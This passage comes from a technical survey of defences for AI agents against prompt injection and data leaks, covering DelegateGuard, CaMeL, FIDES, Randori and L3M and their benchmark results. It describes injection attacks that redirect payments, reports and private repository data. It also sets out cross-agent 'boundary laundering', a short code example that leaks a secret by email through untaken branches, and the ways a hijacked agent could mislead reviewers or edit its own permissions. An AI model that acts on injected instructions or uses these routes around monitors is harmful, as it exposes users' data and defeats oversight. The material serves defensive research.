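labels(*c*) ⊆ labels(*p*), operations(*c*) ⊆ operations(*p*), destinations(*c*) ⊆ destinations(*p*), depth(*c*) < depth(*p*)

and its purpose must fall within the parent's. The symbol ⊆ means that everything in the first set is also in the second. If the user cancels the task, the monitor treats the original grant and everything descended from it as invalid. A worker that wakes up an hour later can't act on old permission.

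The tests used five office workflows, such as sorting email and reviewing code. In conversations between agents running a small open model, attacks caused leaks in 38 of 45 runs with no protection and 9 of 45 with DelegateGuard. The monitor didn't block any legitimate task. All nine leaks came from code review, where the agent's job is to post comments that outsiders can read.

Tran-Truong and colleagues prove that no monitor of this kind could have stopped those leaks. DelegateGuard doesn't read the content of messages, so if it allows a harmless comment in a public place, it must also allow one that contains a secret. A monitor that searched messages for the secret stopped every leak in a separate set of 26 attacks, but also blocked four of five legitimate actions.

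A fixed list of permitted destinations did as well as DelegateGuard on those 26 attacks, with three leaks each. DelegateGuard, the more elaborate system, also blocked ten other cases that the fixed list allowed. In five, a worker tried to finish its job after the user had cancelled it, and in the other five, a worker tried to send the wrong data to a permitted destination. Blocking the wrong data requires correct labels, and some of the 26 attacks were attempts to get round the monitor by declaring that a message contained no labelled data.

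The design depends on the first grant. When the researchers added one outside web address to it, as someone might for convenience, 30 of 45 attacks succeeded. The monitor still stopped the other 15, which relied on cancelled permission.

### Why these languages stayed rare

Object-capability languages have existed for decades, but few programmers use them. Habitat Chronicles attributes this mainly to the amount of software that already exists. Most libraries assume that any code can open a file or a network connection. Someone has to prune or wrap these libraries before safe code can use them, and programmers find the pruned versions awkward. A program designed around references also has to pass each reference from its starting point through every function that needs it, which can mean reorganising all the code.

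Some of the benefits also require other organisations to change. In 2017, the budgeting service Mint collected its customers' bank passwords to read their balances. A read-only token from each bank would have been enough. According to Habitat Chronicles, there was no technical obstacle, but the banks and services would all have had to agree on a standard and rebuild their systems.

Object-capability languages are easier to adopt when agents write the code. The agent writes most of it from scratch, so there is less old code to convert, and the tedious work of passing references through many functions falls to the model instead of a human programmer. TACIT needs about 1,000 lines of shared library code, plus a few hundred lines to describe the tools for each new kind of work. Only work on the shared library requires knowing Scala's capability features well. Checking a typical program takes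 less than a second.

The savings are smaller for an agent that works on existing software. A coding agent on a Python project has to run the project's tests, which are Python programs outside the compiler's control. Scala's capture checking is still experimental. Researchers have proved its basic rules sound with computer-checked proofs, but Odersky and colleagues have yet to prove that the restricted version they use for agents provides all its guarantees. That version trusts any library code that a programmer has marked as safe, so a single mistaken mark could let every agent bypass the rules.

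## CaMeL: tracking where each value came from

Scala's compiler can keep a secret away from code that would leak it, but it doesn't record whether an account number came from the company's supplier register or from a stranger's email. A system that checks where data came from needs a rule for mixing trustworthy and untrustworthy data. The usual starting point is a model that Kenneth Biba developed at the MITRE Corporation in the 1970s.

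Biba gave every program and every piece of data an integrity level. Under his strict policy, a program may read only data at its own level or higher, and may change only data at its own level or lower. Data therefore can't influence anything at a higher level than its own. Suppose there are two levels, trusted for the manager's request and the ledger, and untrusted for web pages and incoming emails. The payment agent needs the trusted level to update the ledger, so it may not read the supplier's email.

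Biba also described a looser policy, the low-water mark. A program may read anything, but its level drops to that of the least trusted data it has read. The payment agent could open the email, but it couldn't write to the ledger afterwards. Since anything in the prompt may affect the next tool call, reading a single web page lowers the agent's level for the rest of the conversation.

In *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control*, Costa, Köpf and colleagues at Microsoft (2025) restricted the more consequential tools of an ordinary GPT-4o agent once untrusted data had entered its prompt. The share of simulated banking tasks the agent completed fell from 98.8% to 37.5%, and the share of tasks in the messaging program Slack fell from 93.3% to 20.0%. Completion of travel tasks hardly fell, because the policy let many travel tools run after the agent had read untrusted data, as long as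 nothing confidential leaked.

### A plan written before the agent reads anything

CaMeL keeps untrusted text out of the prompt that decides what to do. Debenedetti and colleagues at Google DeepMind presented it in *Defeating Prompt Injections by Design* (2025). They built on a 2023 proposal by the developer Simon Willison to divide an agent between two models, one that plans and one that reads. Willison (2025) explains the result in *CaMeL offers a promising new direction for mitigating prompt injection attacks*. A request goes through these steps:

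1. The planning model receives the user's request and a description of the tools. It writes the whole job as a program in a restricted version of Python.
2. A purpose-built interpreter runs the program. It stores the result of each tool call in a variable, and the planning model never sees the contents.
3. When the program needs a fact from free text, such as a date or an address, it asks the reading model. This model has no tools, and the program can specify the form of its answer.
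4. The interpreter tags every value with its sources and with the people allowed to read it.
5. Before each tool call, the interpreter compares the arguments' tags with a policy for that tool. It then runs the call, refuses it or asks the user.

Tags have to survive calculation, or an attacker's text would look clean as soon as the program copied part of it. If the program computes *z* from *x* and *y*, the usual rule is

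sources(*z*) = sources(*x*) ∪ sources(*y*), readers(*z*) = readers(*x*) ∩ readers(*y*)

So *z* counts everyone who could have influenced either input, and only people who could read both inputs may read it.

Debenedetti and colleagues call these tags capabilities, and CaMeL is short for "CApabilities for MachinE Learning". They use the word differently from Hardy, because a CaMeL tag doesn't give its holder access to anything. It only describes the value so that CaMeL can apply a policy to it, which makes the tag closer to one of Biba's levels.

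### An injected address

Suppose the manager tells the agent, "Send the damage report to the chair supplier's complaints address. It's in their last email." The planning model might write this program:

```python
message = get_last_email(sender="chair supplier")
address = ask_reader("Find the complaints address", message,
                     returns=EmailAddress)
report  = get_file("damage-report.pdf")
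send_email(to=address, subject="Broken chairs", attachment=report)
```

An attacker with access to the supplier's mailbox has added a sentence to that email telling AI agents to forward the payroll. The attack fails even if the sentence fools the reading model, because that model has no tools and the program contains no line that opens the payroll.

A cleverer attacker replaces the complaints address with their own. The program calls the reading model to find the address, so the model returns the false one, and the plan's steps don't change. Under Willison's original proposal, the report would go to the attacker, a flaw that Willison credits the DeepMind team with finding. CaMeL still has the tags that record where the address came from.

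| Value | Sources | Permitted readers |
|---|---|---|
| `message` | An email from outside | The manager and the supplier |
| `address` | The same email, through the reading model | The manager and the supplier |
| `report` | The company's files | Staff and the supplier's registered contact |

Suppose the policy for `send_email` requires that the recipient's address come from the user or the company's address book, and that every recipient be permitted to read the attachment. The attacker's address fails both tests, so the interpreter stops and asks the manager. Rajani and colleagues had shown that labels of this kind stop an outsider's value from reaching a protected place, which capabilities alone don't do.

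The interpreter would have stopped even if nobody had tampered with the email, because the genuine address would have carried the same source tag. CaMeL can determine that an outsider supplied the address, but not whether the address is correct.

### What the protection costs

Most measurements of CaMeL use *AgentDojo* (2024), a benchmark with 97 tasks and 629 security tests. The tasks take place in a simulated office, bank, Slack workspace and travel service. Each security test pairs a task with an instruction planted in something the agent will read. A program then checks whether the agent completed the user's task and whether it achieved the attacker's goal.

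The benchmark's attacks are fixed and fairly old. Peters-Gill, Semler and colleagues (2026) adapted it for teams of agents in *Can CaMeLs Talk?* and found that attacks succeeded 36.1% of the time against undefended GPT-4.1 agents but never against GPT-5.5. They warn that stronger attacks have beaten every leading model in large public tests. So for recent models, the case for CaMeL depends less on these scores than on keeping the attacker's text away from the planning model.

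This drawback comes partly from planning before reading the data and partly from the policy checks. Garby, Gordon and Sands (2026) separated the two effects in *The LLMbda Calculus* by running CaMeL on the 16 banking tasks, three times each, with its policy checks off and on. They compared it with Randori, their own agent, which also plans before it reads and always has its checks on.

| Banking tasks completed without an attack | GPT-5.2 | MiMo-v2.5 |
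|---|---:|---:|
| CaMeL, policy checks off | 32 of 48 | 34 of 48 |
| CaMeL, policy checks on | 18 of 48 | 18 of 48 |
| Randori, checks always on | 36 of 48 | 31 of 48 |

Turning on the policies roughly halved the number of tasks CaMeL completed. With them on, no attack succeeded in any run that finished, but with GPT-5.2 only about half of the planned attack runs finished. The 37.5% completion rate is also uncertain by about 27 percentage points either way, because it is based on only sixteen tasks.

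Better models lose less performance when they have to plan without seeing the data. Peters-Gill and colleagues tested five models, with policies off, on 112 industrial maintenance tasks that a coordinating agent shares among four others. CaMeL lowered completion by 21.6 percentage points on average, but by 13.4 for the two strongest models, Claude Fable 5 and GPT-5.5. There is less reason to expect better models to reduce the losses caused by policies, because a policy that forbids paying an account named in a file stops the agent from paying the bill in that file, however capable its model is.

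Other tests give very different completion rates. When Ma and Schmid ran CaMeL's released code through an adapter, it completed only 29 of AgentDojo's 97 tasks with no attack, compared with 59 for SecureClaw. In tests by Odersky and colleagues, CaMeL's score varied widely with the model and the kind of task. The setup may explain some of these differences. AgentDojo's tool descriptions don't specify the format of each tool's results. An ordinary agent can learn the format by looking at the results, but CaMeL's planning model has to write code for results it will never see, so Peters-Gill and colleagues added the formats to every description. They consider this a small job that a company would do once for each set of tools.

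CaMeL also uses more computation. According to *Indirect Prompt Injections* (2025), the median AgentDojo task with GPT-4o needed 2.82 times as much input text and 2.73 times as much output as with no defence. In *CaMeLs Can Use Computers Too* (2026), which applies the design to agents that operate a desktop, 17 tasks cost $5.40 in model fees. Most of that paid for the planning model, whose plans must be long enough to cover every situation the agent might meet on screen. A version with an extra consistency check cost $11.57.

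### When the next step depends on what the agent reads

A CaMeL program can contain branches, but only ones that the planning model wrote in advance. Suppose the manager asks the agent to read the supplier's email and deal with whatever it raises. The email might ask for a photograph of the broken chairs, a new delivery date or a signature. An ordinary agent would read the email and then choose a tool, but CaMeL's planning model would have to write a branch for each of these requests before the email was read.

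Peters-Gill and colleagues attribute most of the failed tasks in their tests to this. They also describe a less obvious failure, in which an agent asked for a machine's readings over certain dates couldn't find them and returned readings for nearby dates instead. The program above it, written before anyone knew this would happen, continued as if the data were correct.

Costa and colleagues classified AgentDojo's tasks by whether the right sequence of actions depends on what the agent finds. It does in 5% of the office tasks and 10% of the travel tasks, but in more than 40% of the banking and Slack tasks. CaMeL would therefore limit an assistant that forwards and summarises documents much less than one that acts on what they say.

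Their own system, FIDES, lets the agent plan as it goes. Each message and tool result has one label for how trustworthy it is and another for who may read it. When a tool returns something less trustworthy than the conversation so far, FIDES stores that part in a variable and shows the model only the variable's name. An email's date might stay visible while its body is hidden. This avoids the low-water mark problem, because the hidden text hasn't influenced the model.

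If the model needs to know what a variable contains, it can open the variable and accept the lower level for the rest of the conversation, or it can question a separate model that has no tools and restrict the form of the answer. For example, a user asks the agent to check three emails for a meeting request and add any meeting to the calendar. The agent asks the separate model whether there is a request, and allows only "true" or "false". If the agent reads "true", it has the separate model extract the details into another variable, then passes that variable to the calendar tool without opening it.

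An attacker can't fit an instruction into "true" or "false", so a policy may reasonably let the agent act on the answer. But the answer can still be wrong, and a wrong answer about whether the dispute over the chairs has ended would release $12,400.

With its policies on, FIDES stopped every attack in AgentDojo that Costa and colleagues considered genuine. The benchmark's own program counted three successful attacks, but they judged each to be harmless or a scoring error. With GPT-4o, FIDES completed an average of 50% of tasks across the four settings, compared with 84% for the undefended agent and 42% for the agent that lost its level after one untrusted read. A stronger model helped here too, as replacing GPT-4o with OpenAI's o1 raised FIDES's travel score from 41% to 68%.

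These results come from 2024 models. Costa and colleagues did not test the restricted answers, the part of FIDES that best addresses unpredictable tasks, because few AgentDojo tasks needed them, so that part has the least evidence. They also labelled as untrusted exactly the fields that the benchmark's attacks used. A company would have to decide for itself which fields an attacker could reach.

### False content that leaves the plan unchanged

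Garby and colleagues divided the 144 pairs of banking tasks and attacks into two groups. In 97 pairs, the attacker needs an action that the user's task would never include, such as a payment during a request to summarise transactions. Planning in advance generally defeats these attacks without any policy. In the other 47, the plan already includes the tool the attacker wants, and safety depends on which values are passed to it.

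Randori resisted all but 2 of 1,296 attack runs. In both failures, the user asked the agent to make the payment described in a file, but an attacker had already replaced the file. The agent paid as the file instructed. The DeepMind team encountered the same case with CaMeL and did not count it among the attacks CaMeL is meant to stop. The attacker hasn't diverted the agent from its task, because the user chose to let the file determine the payment.

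CaMeL's other failure in its original evaluation came from an agent quoting a hotel review, as did TACIT's only failure. Costa and colleagues point out that an email could also contain instructions for the reading model to produce an empty summary, which would reach the right person at the right time but without the news they needed. Tags can show the recipient that the summary came from outside emails, but not what it left out.

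A planning model can also weaken the protection by writing a plan that is too general. In one banking task, the agent has to read a file and follow its instructions precisely. With policies off, CaMeL's planning model wrote a loop with a branch for every tool, so that the program could follow any instructions in the file. An attacker's file could then trigger any tool, even though the planning model had never read the file.

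### Writing policies and answering questions

Somebody has to decide which sources each tool may trust, and the DeepMind team lists this work among CaMeL's main limitations. Willison, who has worked on application security for two decades, says he has trouble with such policies and is nervous about any system that requires ordinary users to think about them.

*Formal Policy Enforcement for Agentic Systems* (Palumbo, Choudhary and colleagues, 2026) describes FORGE, a monitor that records what each action depended on, including actions by other agents. A rule can be short if someone has already classified the data. For example, one FORGE rule blocks a message to an outsider if the message depends on both untrusted input and secret data. The rule allows messages that depend on only one of these, so an agent may still send a public brochure after reading a stranger's email. On AgentDojo, FORGE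 was about as secure as stricter tracking and completed substantially more tasks. It can also translate a policy from English into formal rules, but its guarantees assume that the resulting rules express what the user wanted.

When a policy can't settle a case, the user has to decide. Garby and colleagues' results suggest this would happen often, since the checks blocked so many legitimate banking tasks. People who approve nearly every prompt will probably approve the attacker's complaints address as well. CaMeL can at least show them a prompt that explains the risk, such as "Send the damage report to an address that appears only in this email?" instead of "Allow `send_email`?"

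Randori asks fewer questions by letting the planning model make exceptions, called endorsements. If the user asks the agent to pay the bill in a file, the model can mark the file's contents as acceptable for that payment. It must do this while writing the program, before any outside text can influence it. When Garby and colleagues removed this option, the number of runs completed with Qwen3.7-plus fell from 36 to 30 out of 48. Both successful attacks on Randori depended on an endorsement.

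This is a sensible tradeoff for a company worried about prompt injection. It offers less protection against a careless or misaligned planning model, which could endorse anything. A harness could require endorsements that affect payments to be approved by a person, who would at least review a specific exception before the agent acted.

### Gaps in the tracking

The tags work only if the interpreter keeps track of them. Garby and colleagues found that CaMeL's interpreter could treat an untrusted value as trusted after the program inserted it into longer text. Inserting values into text is very common in programming, so a model could trigger the fault by accident.

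They also describe a leak through code that doesn't run. This program, a version of a puzzle known since the 1970s, reveals whether an account holds more than $100,000:

```python
tell  = True
small = True
if balance > 100000:
    small = False
if small:
    tell = False
if tell:
    send_email(to="outsider@example.com", body="rich")
```

CaMeL tags a variable as secret when the program changes it inside a branch that depends on a secret. If the balance is high, `small` becomes false and gets the tag. The program then skips the line that would have changed `tell`, so `tell` never gets a tag, and the email goes out. If the balance is low, no email goes out, so the outsider learns whether the balance is high from whether the email arrives. An attacker who can only plant text in emails couldn't easily exploit this, because the planning model writes the code without seeing that text. The leak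 matters more if the planning model itself is hostile.

CaMeL's retries after errors happen outside the interpreter and are another source of leaks. Whether a policy blocked an attempt can reveal one bit about a secret, and repeated attempts could reveal all of it. Randori retries in a practice run with invented data, and uses real data only once its program is ready. Garby and colleagues proved in Lean, a language for computer-checked proofs, that their interpreter tracks labels correctly. The proof doesn't cover what an observer could learn from a program that never finishes. FIDES has a narrower guarantee, which covers direct copying of data but not what someone could infer from the order of the agent's tool calls. Costa and colleagues considered a stronger guarantee too restrictive to be useful.

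### When one CaMeL agent instructs another

CaMeL treats whatever its user writes as trusted. When one agent delegates work to another, the first agent is the second one's user, so CaMeL would also trust any text from a stranger in the first agent's instructions. Peters-Gill and colleagues call this failure "boundary laundering". Louck's attacks similarly hid the origin of text by passing it through an agent's memory.

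In their demonstration, a user asks a coordinating agent to send Julie a summary of some job applicants on Slack. A database agent fetches the records, one of which contains an instruction to email the data to an outside address. Neither agent's planning model sees that record, and neither plan changes. The coordinating agent then sends a notification agent the message "Send this summary to Julie via Slack", followed by the summary. The notification agent's planning model treats the whole message as a request from its user and writes a program that messages Julie and also emails the outside address.

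All three agents ran GPT-5.2 under CaMeL with no policies. A policy on `send_email` wouldn't necessarily have helped, because the notification agent would have treated the address as coming from its user. In the multi-agent version of AgentDojo, attacks on separate CaMeL agents succeeded in at most 0.5% of trials, but those attacks weren't written to cross this boundary, and every one that succeeded did cross it.

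Peters-Gill and colleagues' remedy, multi-CaMeL, splits each delegated task into an instruction, such as "Send the provided content to the recipient", and a set of variables with their tags still attached. The receiving agent's planning model reads the instruction but can't read the variables. The interpreter rejects any instruction that depends on the result of a tool call. With multi-CaMeL, no attack in the benchmark succeeded. Completion of the industrial tasks fell by a further 3.2 percentage points on average, and by less than one point for the two strongest models.

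The remedy depends on the interpreter tracking every dependency, so information can still leak through code that doesn't run. It also covers only agents arranged in a tree, where each takes instructions from a single parent. Agents that share a task list or write to one another freely have no clear boundary where an interpreter could separate instructions from data.

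## L3M: a runtime that joins capabilities with separation of duties

CaMeL's protection depends on keeping untrusted text away from the planning model. L3M is designed on the assumption that this defense has already failed. In its threat model, an attacker chooses the agent's next tool calls, and L3M is meant to limit the damage those calls can do.

L3M is an open-source harness for teams of long-running agents. Researchers at Amazon released it in autumn 2026 and describe it in the paper *L3M*. It gives agents unforgeable tokens, as object-capability languages do, and divides risky jobs between parties, as Clark and Wilson recommended.

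The researchers wrote L3M in Lean, the proof language that Garby and colleagues used. People can also write ordinary software in Lean, so the researchers could prove properties of the same code that runs the agents. If a later change to the code makes a proof fail, the program won't build. Amazon, which also funds Lean's development, argues that testing covers only the cases somebody thought of, while a proof covers every input, as reported in Computer Weekly's *AWS bets big on Lean programming language to bring mathematical guarantees*. But a proof covers only the property it states, and L3M's proofs concern individual checks.

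### From a grant to a system call

Suppose an engineer wants an agent to fix a bug in `record_invoice`. The engineer writes a grant, a record of what the agent may do. It lets the agent work in the project's folder and on its own branches in the project's Git repository, push those branches to the company's server, and read one documentation website. It doesn't give the agent a shell. The harness keeps the grant where the agent can't change it.

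When the agent starts, the harness makes one token for each kind of access in the grant. The file token lists the permitted folders, the Git token lists the permitted branches and servers, and the network token lists the permitted websites; there is no shell token.

A tool can affect the outside world only through functions that take a token as an argument. In simplified form, the function for fetching a web page has this type, where `NetCap` is the network token:

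```
fetch : NetCap → Request → Response
```

Each tool comes with a list of the kinds of access it uses. The harness offers the model only the tools that the agent's tokens cover, so this agent's tool list doesn't include a shell.

When the model requests a page, the web tool checks the address against the websites listed on the token before sending anything. The module that makes the system call then checks the address again. For files, the first check rejects a path like `../payroll/salaries.csv` from its text alone. The second catches symbolic links, which look like ordinary files but point to another location.

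Another check runs every time someone builds L3M. It rejects code that creates a token outside the one module allowed to create it, and code that bypasses the tokens by writing to a file directly.

These tokens are broader than the capabilities Hardy had in mind. The model still names a page as text, and the harness supplies the token. The network token covers every page on the documentation site, so injected text can influence which page the agent requests and what the request contains, but it can't give the agent access to another website. If a file in the repository contains an instruction allowing agents to push to the main branch, the model may try, but the push fails because the file doesn't change the grant.

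### Passing authority to a child agent

The agent might delegate writing tests to a child agent. The harness looks up the parent's grant and compares it with the one requested for the child. If the requested grant includes a second website that the parent can't reach, the harness refuses the whole request.

The researchers proved that this comparison works for every pair of grants. If *P* is the parent's grant and *R* is a proposed role for the child, then *P* ∧ *R* contains only what both allow, and the theorem states that

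*P* ∧ *R* ≤ *P*

where ≤ means "allows no more than". They also proved that no agent can issue a grant to itself.

The limit applies when the parent creates the child. Later, a grandparent can give the child any access the grandparent itself holds, even if the parent lacks it, and a person can give the child any access at all.

The limit doesn't extend unchanged to a whole family of agents. A descendant can have access beyond the first agent's recorded grant, because a child also gets access to its parent's own branches, which the parent's recorded grant doesn't list. The paper gives a counterexample to the unchanged limit and proves a corrected version that allows for this additional access.

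A parent lends part of its budget to its children. If it has 100 model calls left and lends 40 to each of two children, it keeps 20, and a third loan of 40 fails. In general, the children's limits plus what the parent keeps can't exceed what the parent had. This avoids the problem with Atlas, the travel agent whose separate tokens could add up to more than its budget. The proof covers only one batch of loans, and extending it to a whole run would take further work. L3M's budget counts model calls, so a company would need a separate account for money.

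### Tools that agents write for themselves

An agent that repeats the same steps can turn them into a tool. In the paper's example, an agent writes a short Lean program that counts the "TODO" comments in a project. The next time the agent starts, the harness checks the program and adds it to the tool list.

The harness checks the program's form before Lean processes it, because processing Lean source can run code. It rejects unsafe features and any attempt to make a token. Lean's type checker then confirms that the program uses only the kinds of access it declares. Finally, the harness compares that declaration with the agent's tokens. The counter declares only that it reads files, so a person can tell from the declaration, without reading the program, that the counter can't send the files anywhere.

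When the tool runs, it uses the tokens the agent already had. The L3M paper summarizes this as "Capability grows; authority does not", where "capability" means what an agent is able to do.

*Agent libOS* (Zhang, 2026) follows the same principle, but checks each operation while the agent runs instead of limiting a new tool through its type. A run-time check can account for recent changes, such as a cancelled permission, while a type check catches an undeclared kind of access before the tool runs. *Agent Harnesses Need Their eBPF* (Wang and Akella, 2026) also describes checks made in advance, but of policies that agents write for how they themselves run. A verifier tests each policy against set rules before loading it.

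L3M therefore lets an agent run a tool it wrote itself, which Clark and Wilson's rules forbid. This is reasonable for a tool that counts comments. If a payment agent wrote `pay_batch` this way, the type checker could confirm that the tool used only the agent's existing access to the payment service, but not that it paid the right invoices. An engineer would still have to certify it.

### Which actions get a review

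L3M runs an action without review if the action is "tame", meaning that the harness can undo it or a token limits where it can reach. The harness can undo a file edit because it saves the old contents in Git beforehand and restores them when the agent is rewound to an earlier turn. It can't undo a web request or a push to a server, but these are still tame if a token limits their reach, because a person accepted that reach when writing the grant.

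| Action | Harness can undo it | Token limits its reach | Default |
|---|---|---|---|
| Edit a file in the agent's folder | Yes | Yes | Runs |
| Fetch a page from a permitted website | No | Yes | Runs |
| Push to a permitted server | No | Yes | Runs |
| Run a command in the offline shell | No | No | Review |
| Run a query on a remote database | No | No | Review |

The harness works out the category from the kinds of access a tool uses, so a programmer can't mark a dangerous tool as tame.

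Limited reach can still allow serious harm. Suppose the company added `pay_invoice` to L3M with a token listing its registered suppliers. Every payment to those suppliers would count as tame, so the agent could pay the disputed $12,400 invoice without review. The company could change the setting to require review of every call, but that would include every file edit.

For a call that needs review, the agent gives its reason and a second model, which has no tools, labels the call "safe" or "wild". If this reviewer can't be reached, the call counts as wild. The reviewer can also suggest a tame alternative, such as L3M's own search tool in place of a shell command. The agent then goes ahead with the call, switches to the alternative or withdraws. To go ahead with a call labeled wild, it has to defend the call, and by default the reviewer answers once more. A person sees the call only if the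 two models still disagree. If nobody is available, the harness rejects the call by default.

L3M shows the agent's prose to the reviewer, whereas Anthropic hid it from auto mode's classifier. This lets an agent clear up a misunderstanding, but it also lets a hijacked agent mislead the reviewer. The L3M researchers acknowledge that a stated reason may leave out where a value came from. They treat review as an extra precaution and rely on the tokens to set the limits.

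### Staged builds

An agent that can both write and run a program could carry out an injected instruction by putting it into the code. L3M's staged builds separate writing the program from running it.

In the simplest version, an agent may edit the Makefile that a `make` command uses, but only a person can approve it. The approval command records a hash of the Makefile, the files it includes and the scripts it calls. Any later edit to these files cancels the approval, and the model can't alter an approved run by supplying arguments.

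A larger build can use two agents:

1. Fetch: the builder downloads outside libraries. It has network access, but this stage contains only the public list of libraries and none of the company's code.
2. Build: the builder compiles the company's code with the network off.
3. Run: a second agent, the runner, runs the finished program. It can't change the program or the code, has no network access and can write only to a new output folder.

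The parent agent identifies the finished program to the runner by its hash. The builder can't run the program and the runner can't modify it, so text injected into either one can't make it both add a back door and run it. If a library is missing during the build, the job fails, because turning the network back on would give one stage both the private code and a way to send it out.

Compiling can also run code, since build scripts and compiler plugins are programs. The sandbox for the build stage must therefore confine them, even though the builder has no permission to run the finished program.

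A matching hash shows only that the runner has the same bytes the builder produced, not that anyone examined them. If the parent passes on every finished program automatically, the back door will run, although only offline and with one folder to write to. A company that wants real separation needs a person or an independent reviewer at the handover. It also has to choose to separate the builder from the runner, because L3M doesn't require it.

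### A quarantined reader

L3M can also separate reading from acting. Suppose an agent sorts bug reports that anyone can submit. It calls a small program, which fetches a report and gives it to a new subagent with an empty grant. The program sends the subagent one question, such as whether the report describes a new fault in the invoice parser. It converts the reply to "yes", "no" or "unclear" and returns only that word to the agent that acts. Any other reply, an error or a timeout becomes "unclear".

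Let *T* be the text of the report, *W* the word and *A* what the acting agent does next. If the text can affect the agent only through the word, then

*I*(*T*; *A*) ≤ *I*(*T*; *W*) ≤ *H*(*W*) ≤ log₂ 3 ≈ 1.58 bits

Here *I* measures how much one thing reveals about another, and *H* measures how uncertain the word is. The first step holds because the agent can't recover information about the report that the word doesn't carry. The last step holds because uncertainty among three possible words is greatest when all three are equally likely.

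The bound assumes that the three words are fixed before the subagent reads the report. How long the call takes and whether it fails must reveal nothing beyond the word, since a subagent that could choose between a fast "yes" and a slow "yes" would have a fourth message. The acting agent also must not open the report by another route. The bound applies to one call, so ten questions about the same report could reveal up to 15.8 bits.

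An attacker can still make the answer wrong, as with the restricted answers in FIDES. A hijacked subagent could answer "no" to every report of a real fault, and the acting agent would ignore those reports.

*Preventing Prompt Injection with Type-Directed Privilege Separation* (Jacob, Alghamdi and colleagues, 2025) tested a looser restriction, under which the reader may return numbers, true-or-false values and choices from a fixed list. No attacks succeeded in the tests. A shopping agent and a calendar agent worked about as well as before, because a review score or a list of meeting times gave them most of the information they needed. An agent that fixed software bugs did much worse, solving 45.0% of cases, down from 68.3% without the restriction. Its reader could pass on the file, the line numbers and the type of bug, but not the user's description of what went wrong.

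*Twin Agent* (Hu, Jacob and colleagues, 2026) lets the reader send short hints in ordinary text. On a similar set of bugs and with the same model, GPT-5.2, the acting agent solved none with nothing from the reader and 62.5% with hints of up to 100 characters, compared with 61.2% for an unrestricted agent. The standard attacks failed, but an attack designed for this system succeeded in 11 of 232 cases. Longer hints made the agent more useful but also easier to attack. A company can therefore reserve the three-word version for yes-or-no decisions.

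L3M's researchers apply the same reasoning to leaks. An agent with access to private code but no network could send questions to a second agent that has network access but no code. If each question has a fixed length of *k* bytes and the agents have no other channel, one question can leak at most 8*k* bits. A 100-byte question can therefore leak at most 800 bits, which is very little of a large program but enough for several passwords. L3M doesn't yet enforce such a limit.

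### Tests on 37 tasks

The researchers measured how the restrictions affected performance on Terminal-Bench, a benchmark that gives an agent a task in a container and checks the result with automatic tests. They used 37 tasks, with three attempts at each, and ran Claude Opus 5 in every set-up. Claude Sonnet 4.6 was the reviewer.

| Set-up | Solved within three attempts | Tokens per successful attempt |
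|---|---:|---:|
| Claude Code without permission checks | 59.5% | 4.4 million |
| L3M with a shell, no review | 41.7% | 7.7 million |
| L3M with a shell, reviewed, disputed calls approved | 40.5% | 12.1 million |
| L3M with a shell, reviewed, disputed calls rejected | 43.2% | 12.8 million |
| L3M with tame tools only | 27.0% | 7.7 million |
| L3M with tame tools, none self-written | 24.3% | 6.2 million |

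The gap between Claude Code and L3M with a shell has several causes. Claude Code could use the network through its shell, and its developers have spent much longer tuning it. The choice of tasks may also have helped Claude Code, since the researchers picked ones it had typically finished within an hour. They stopped each attempt after 75 minutes, while the Terminal-Bench rules allow eight hours, so these scores aren't comparable with the public leaderboard.

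Comparing L3M with and without a shell better shows how much the restrictions reduce performance. The researchers say that tame tools achieve about two thirds of what the shell does, which is correct for tasks solved at least once. Counting every successful attempt, the total fell by roughly half, from 34 with the shell to 18 without it. By either measure, a company that avoided the shell would get much less work done. Self-written tools raised the score by 2.7 percentage points, or one task out of 37.

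Review left success about the same but used roughly 85% more model calls and 50% more tokens. It covered only shell commands, about a quarter of all tool calls. Around 90% of reviewed commands were judged "safe", about 6% led the agent to a milder alternative, and 2.4% ended in disagreement. A person would see only the disagreements, about 0.6% of all tool calls. That is about three in a run of 500, few enough to read carefully.

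The reviewer initially objected to about a third of the commands, and about nine in ten second rounds ended with "safe". The agent may have supplied a fact the reviewer lacked or persuaded it without new facts. The tests can't distinguish the two because they included no attacks or planted mistakes. Nobody has yet published how many harmful commands L3M's reviewer stops, and the proofs don't cover this.

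### What the proofs cover

| Claim | Proved | Assumed or checked in another way |
|---|---|---|
| File tools stay inside the agent's folders | The text of a path can't lead outside them | The harness catches symbolic links at run time |
| Tokens match the grant | Start-up makes no token the grant doesn't provide for | A check on each build stops code from forging tokens |
| A child can't exceed its parent | True when the parent creates the child | Later grants can add authority |
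| Self-written tools add no authority | The program directly names only permitted components | Lean's processing of the code and the modules that make system calls work correctly |
| Undo restores an edited file | The restored bytes match the saved ones | Git returns what it stored |
| Calls that are neither undoable nor limited get a review | True under the default setting | The reviewer judges correctly |

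Even if every assumption holds, these results don't combine into a proof that a whole session is safe. The researchers argue that the checks work together, and they support this with tests. Their argument excludes a grant called "wild", which allows a shell with no sandbox. An agent with that grant could edit its own permissions, and only the review step would stand in its way.

A hijacked agent can also do harm without exceeding an ordinary grant. The agent fixing `record_invoice` could remove the check that compares an invoice's bank account with the supplier register, then push the change to its branch. Both actions are tame. If the project folder contains a password, the agent could copy it into a file and push that too, and L3M can't undo the disclosure. The researchers have designed a meter to record how much of each kind of sensitive data an agent has read and sent, but haven't built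 it. Zhang's system already labels data and checks the labels before the data leaves, though it can't stop an approved recipient from passing the data on.

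## Three incidents tested against the rules

Researchers chose the tasks and attacks used to test L3M and the other systems. This section applies the rules to three messier incidents from 2025 and 2026. In May 2025, researchers demonstrated that a public post on GitHub could lead an agent to disclose its user's private data. In July 2025, an agent from Replit, a platform for building and hosting software, deleted an investor's live database. In June 2026, an agent at OpenAI broke into an Australian government statistics portal.

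Researchers staged the GitHub leak. The other two incidents were real, although the investor got his data back and neither OpenAI nor the Australian government has found evidence that the agent accessed anyone's medical records.

### A public issue and a private repository

Invariant Labs' *GitHub MCP Exploited* (2025) describes a demonstration that matches the GitHub leak Parkinson and colleagues cite. The user had one public and one private repository and had connected Claude Desktop, Anthropic's desktop application, to GitHub through GitHub's official MCP server. Anyone could file an issue, such as a bug report, in the public repository, and the researchers filed one containing instructions for AI agents. When the user asked the agent to look at the issues, it followed those instructions, read private material and put it in a public pull request.

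Heise online's *Attack via GitHub MCP server* explains that the agent could read the private repository because the GitHub MCP server works through the user's own account. The user had granted that access when connecting the server. The data leaked only when the agent wrote to a public place. Willison, in *GitHub MCP Exploited*, says such a leak needs three conditions: access to private data, exposure to malicious instructions and a way to send information out.

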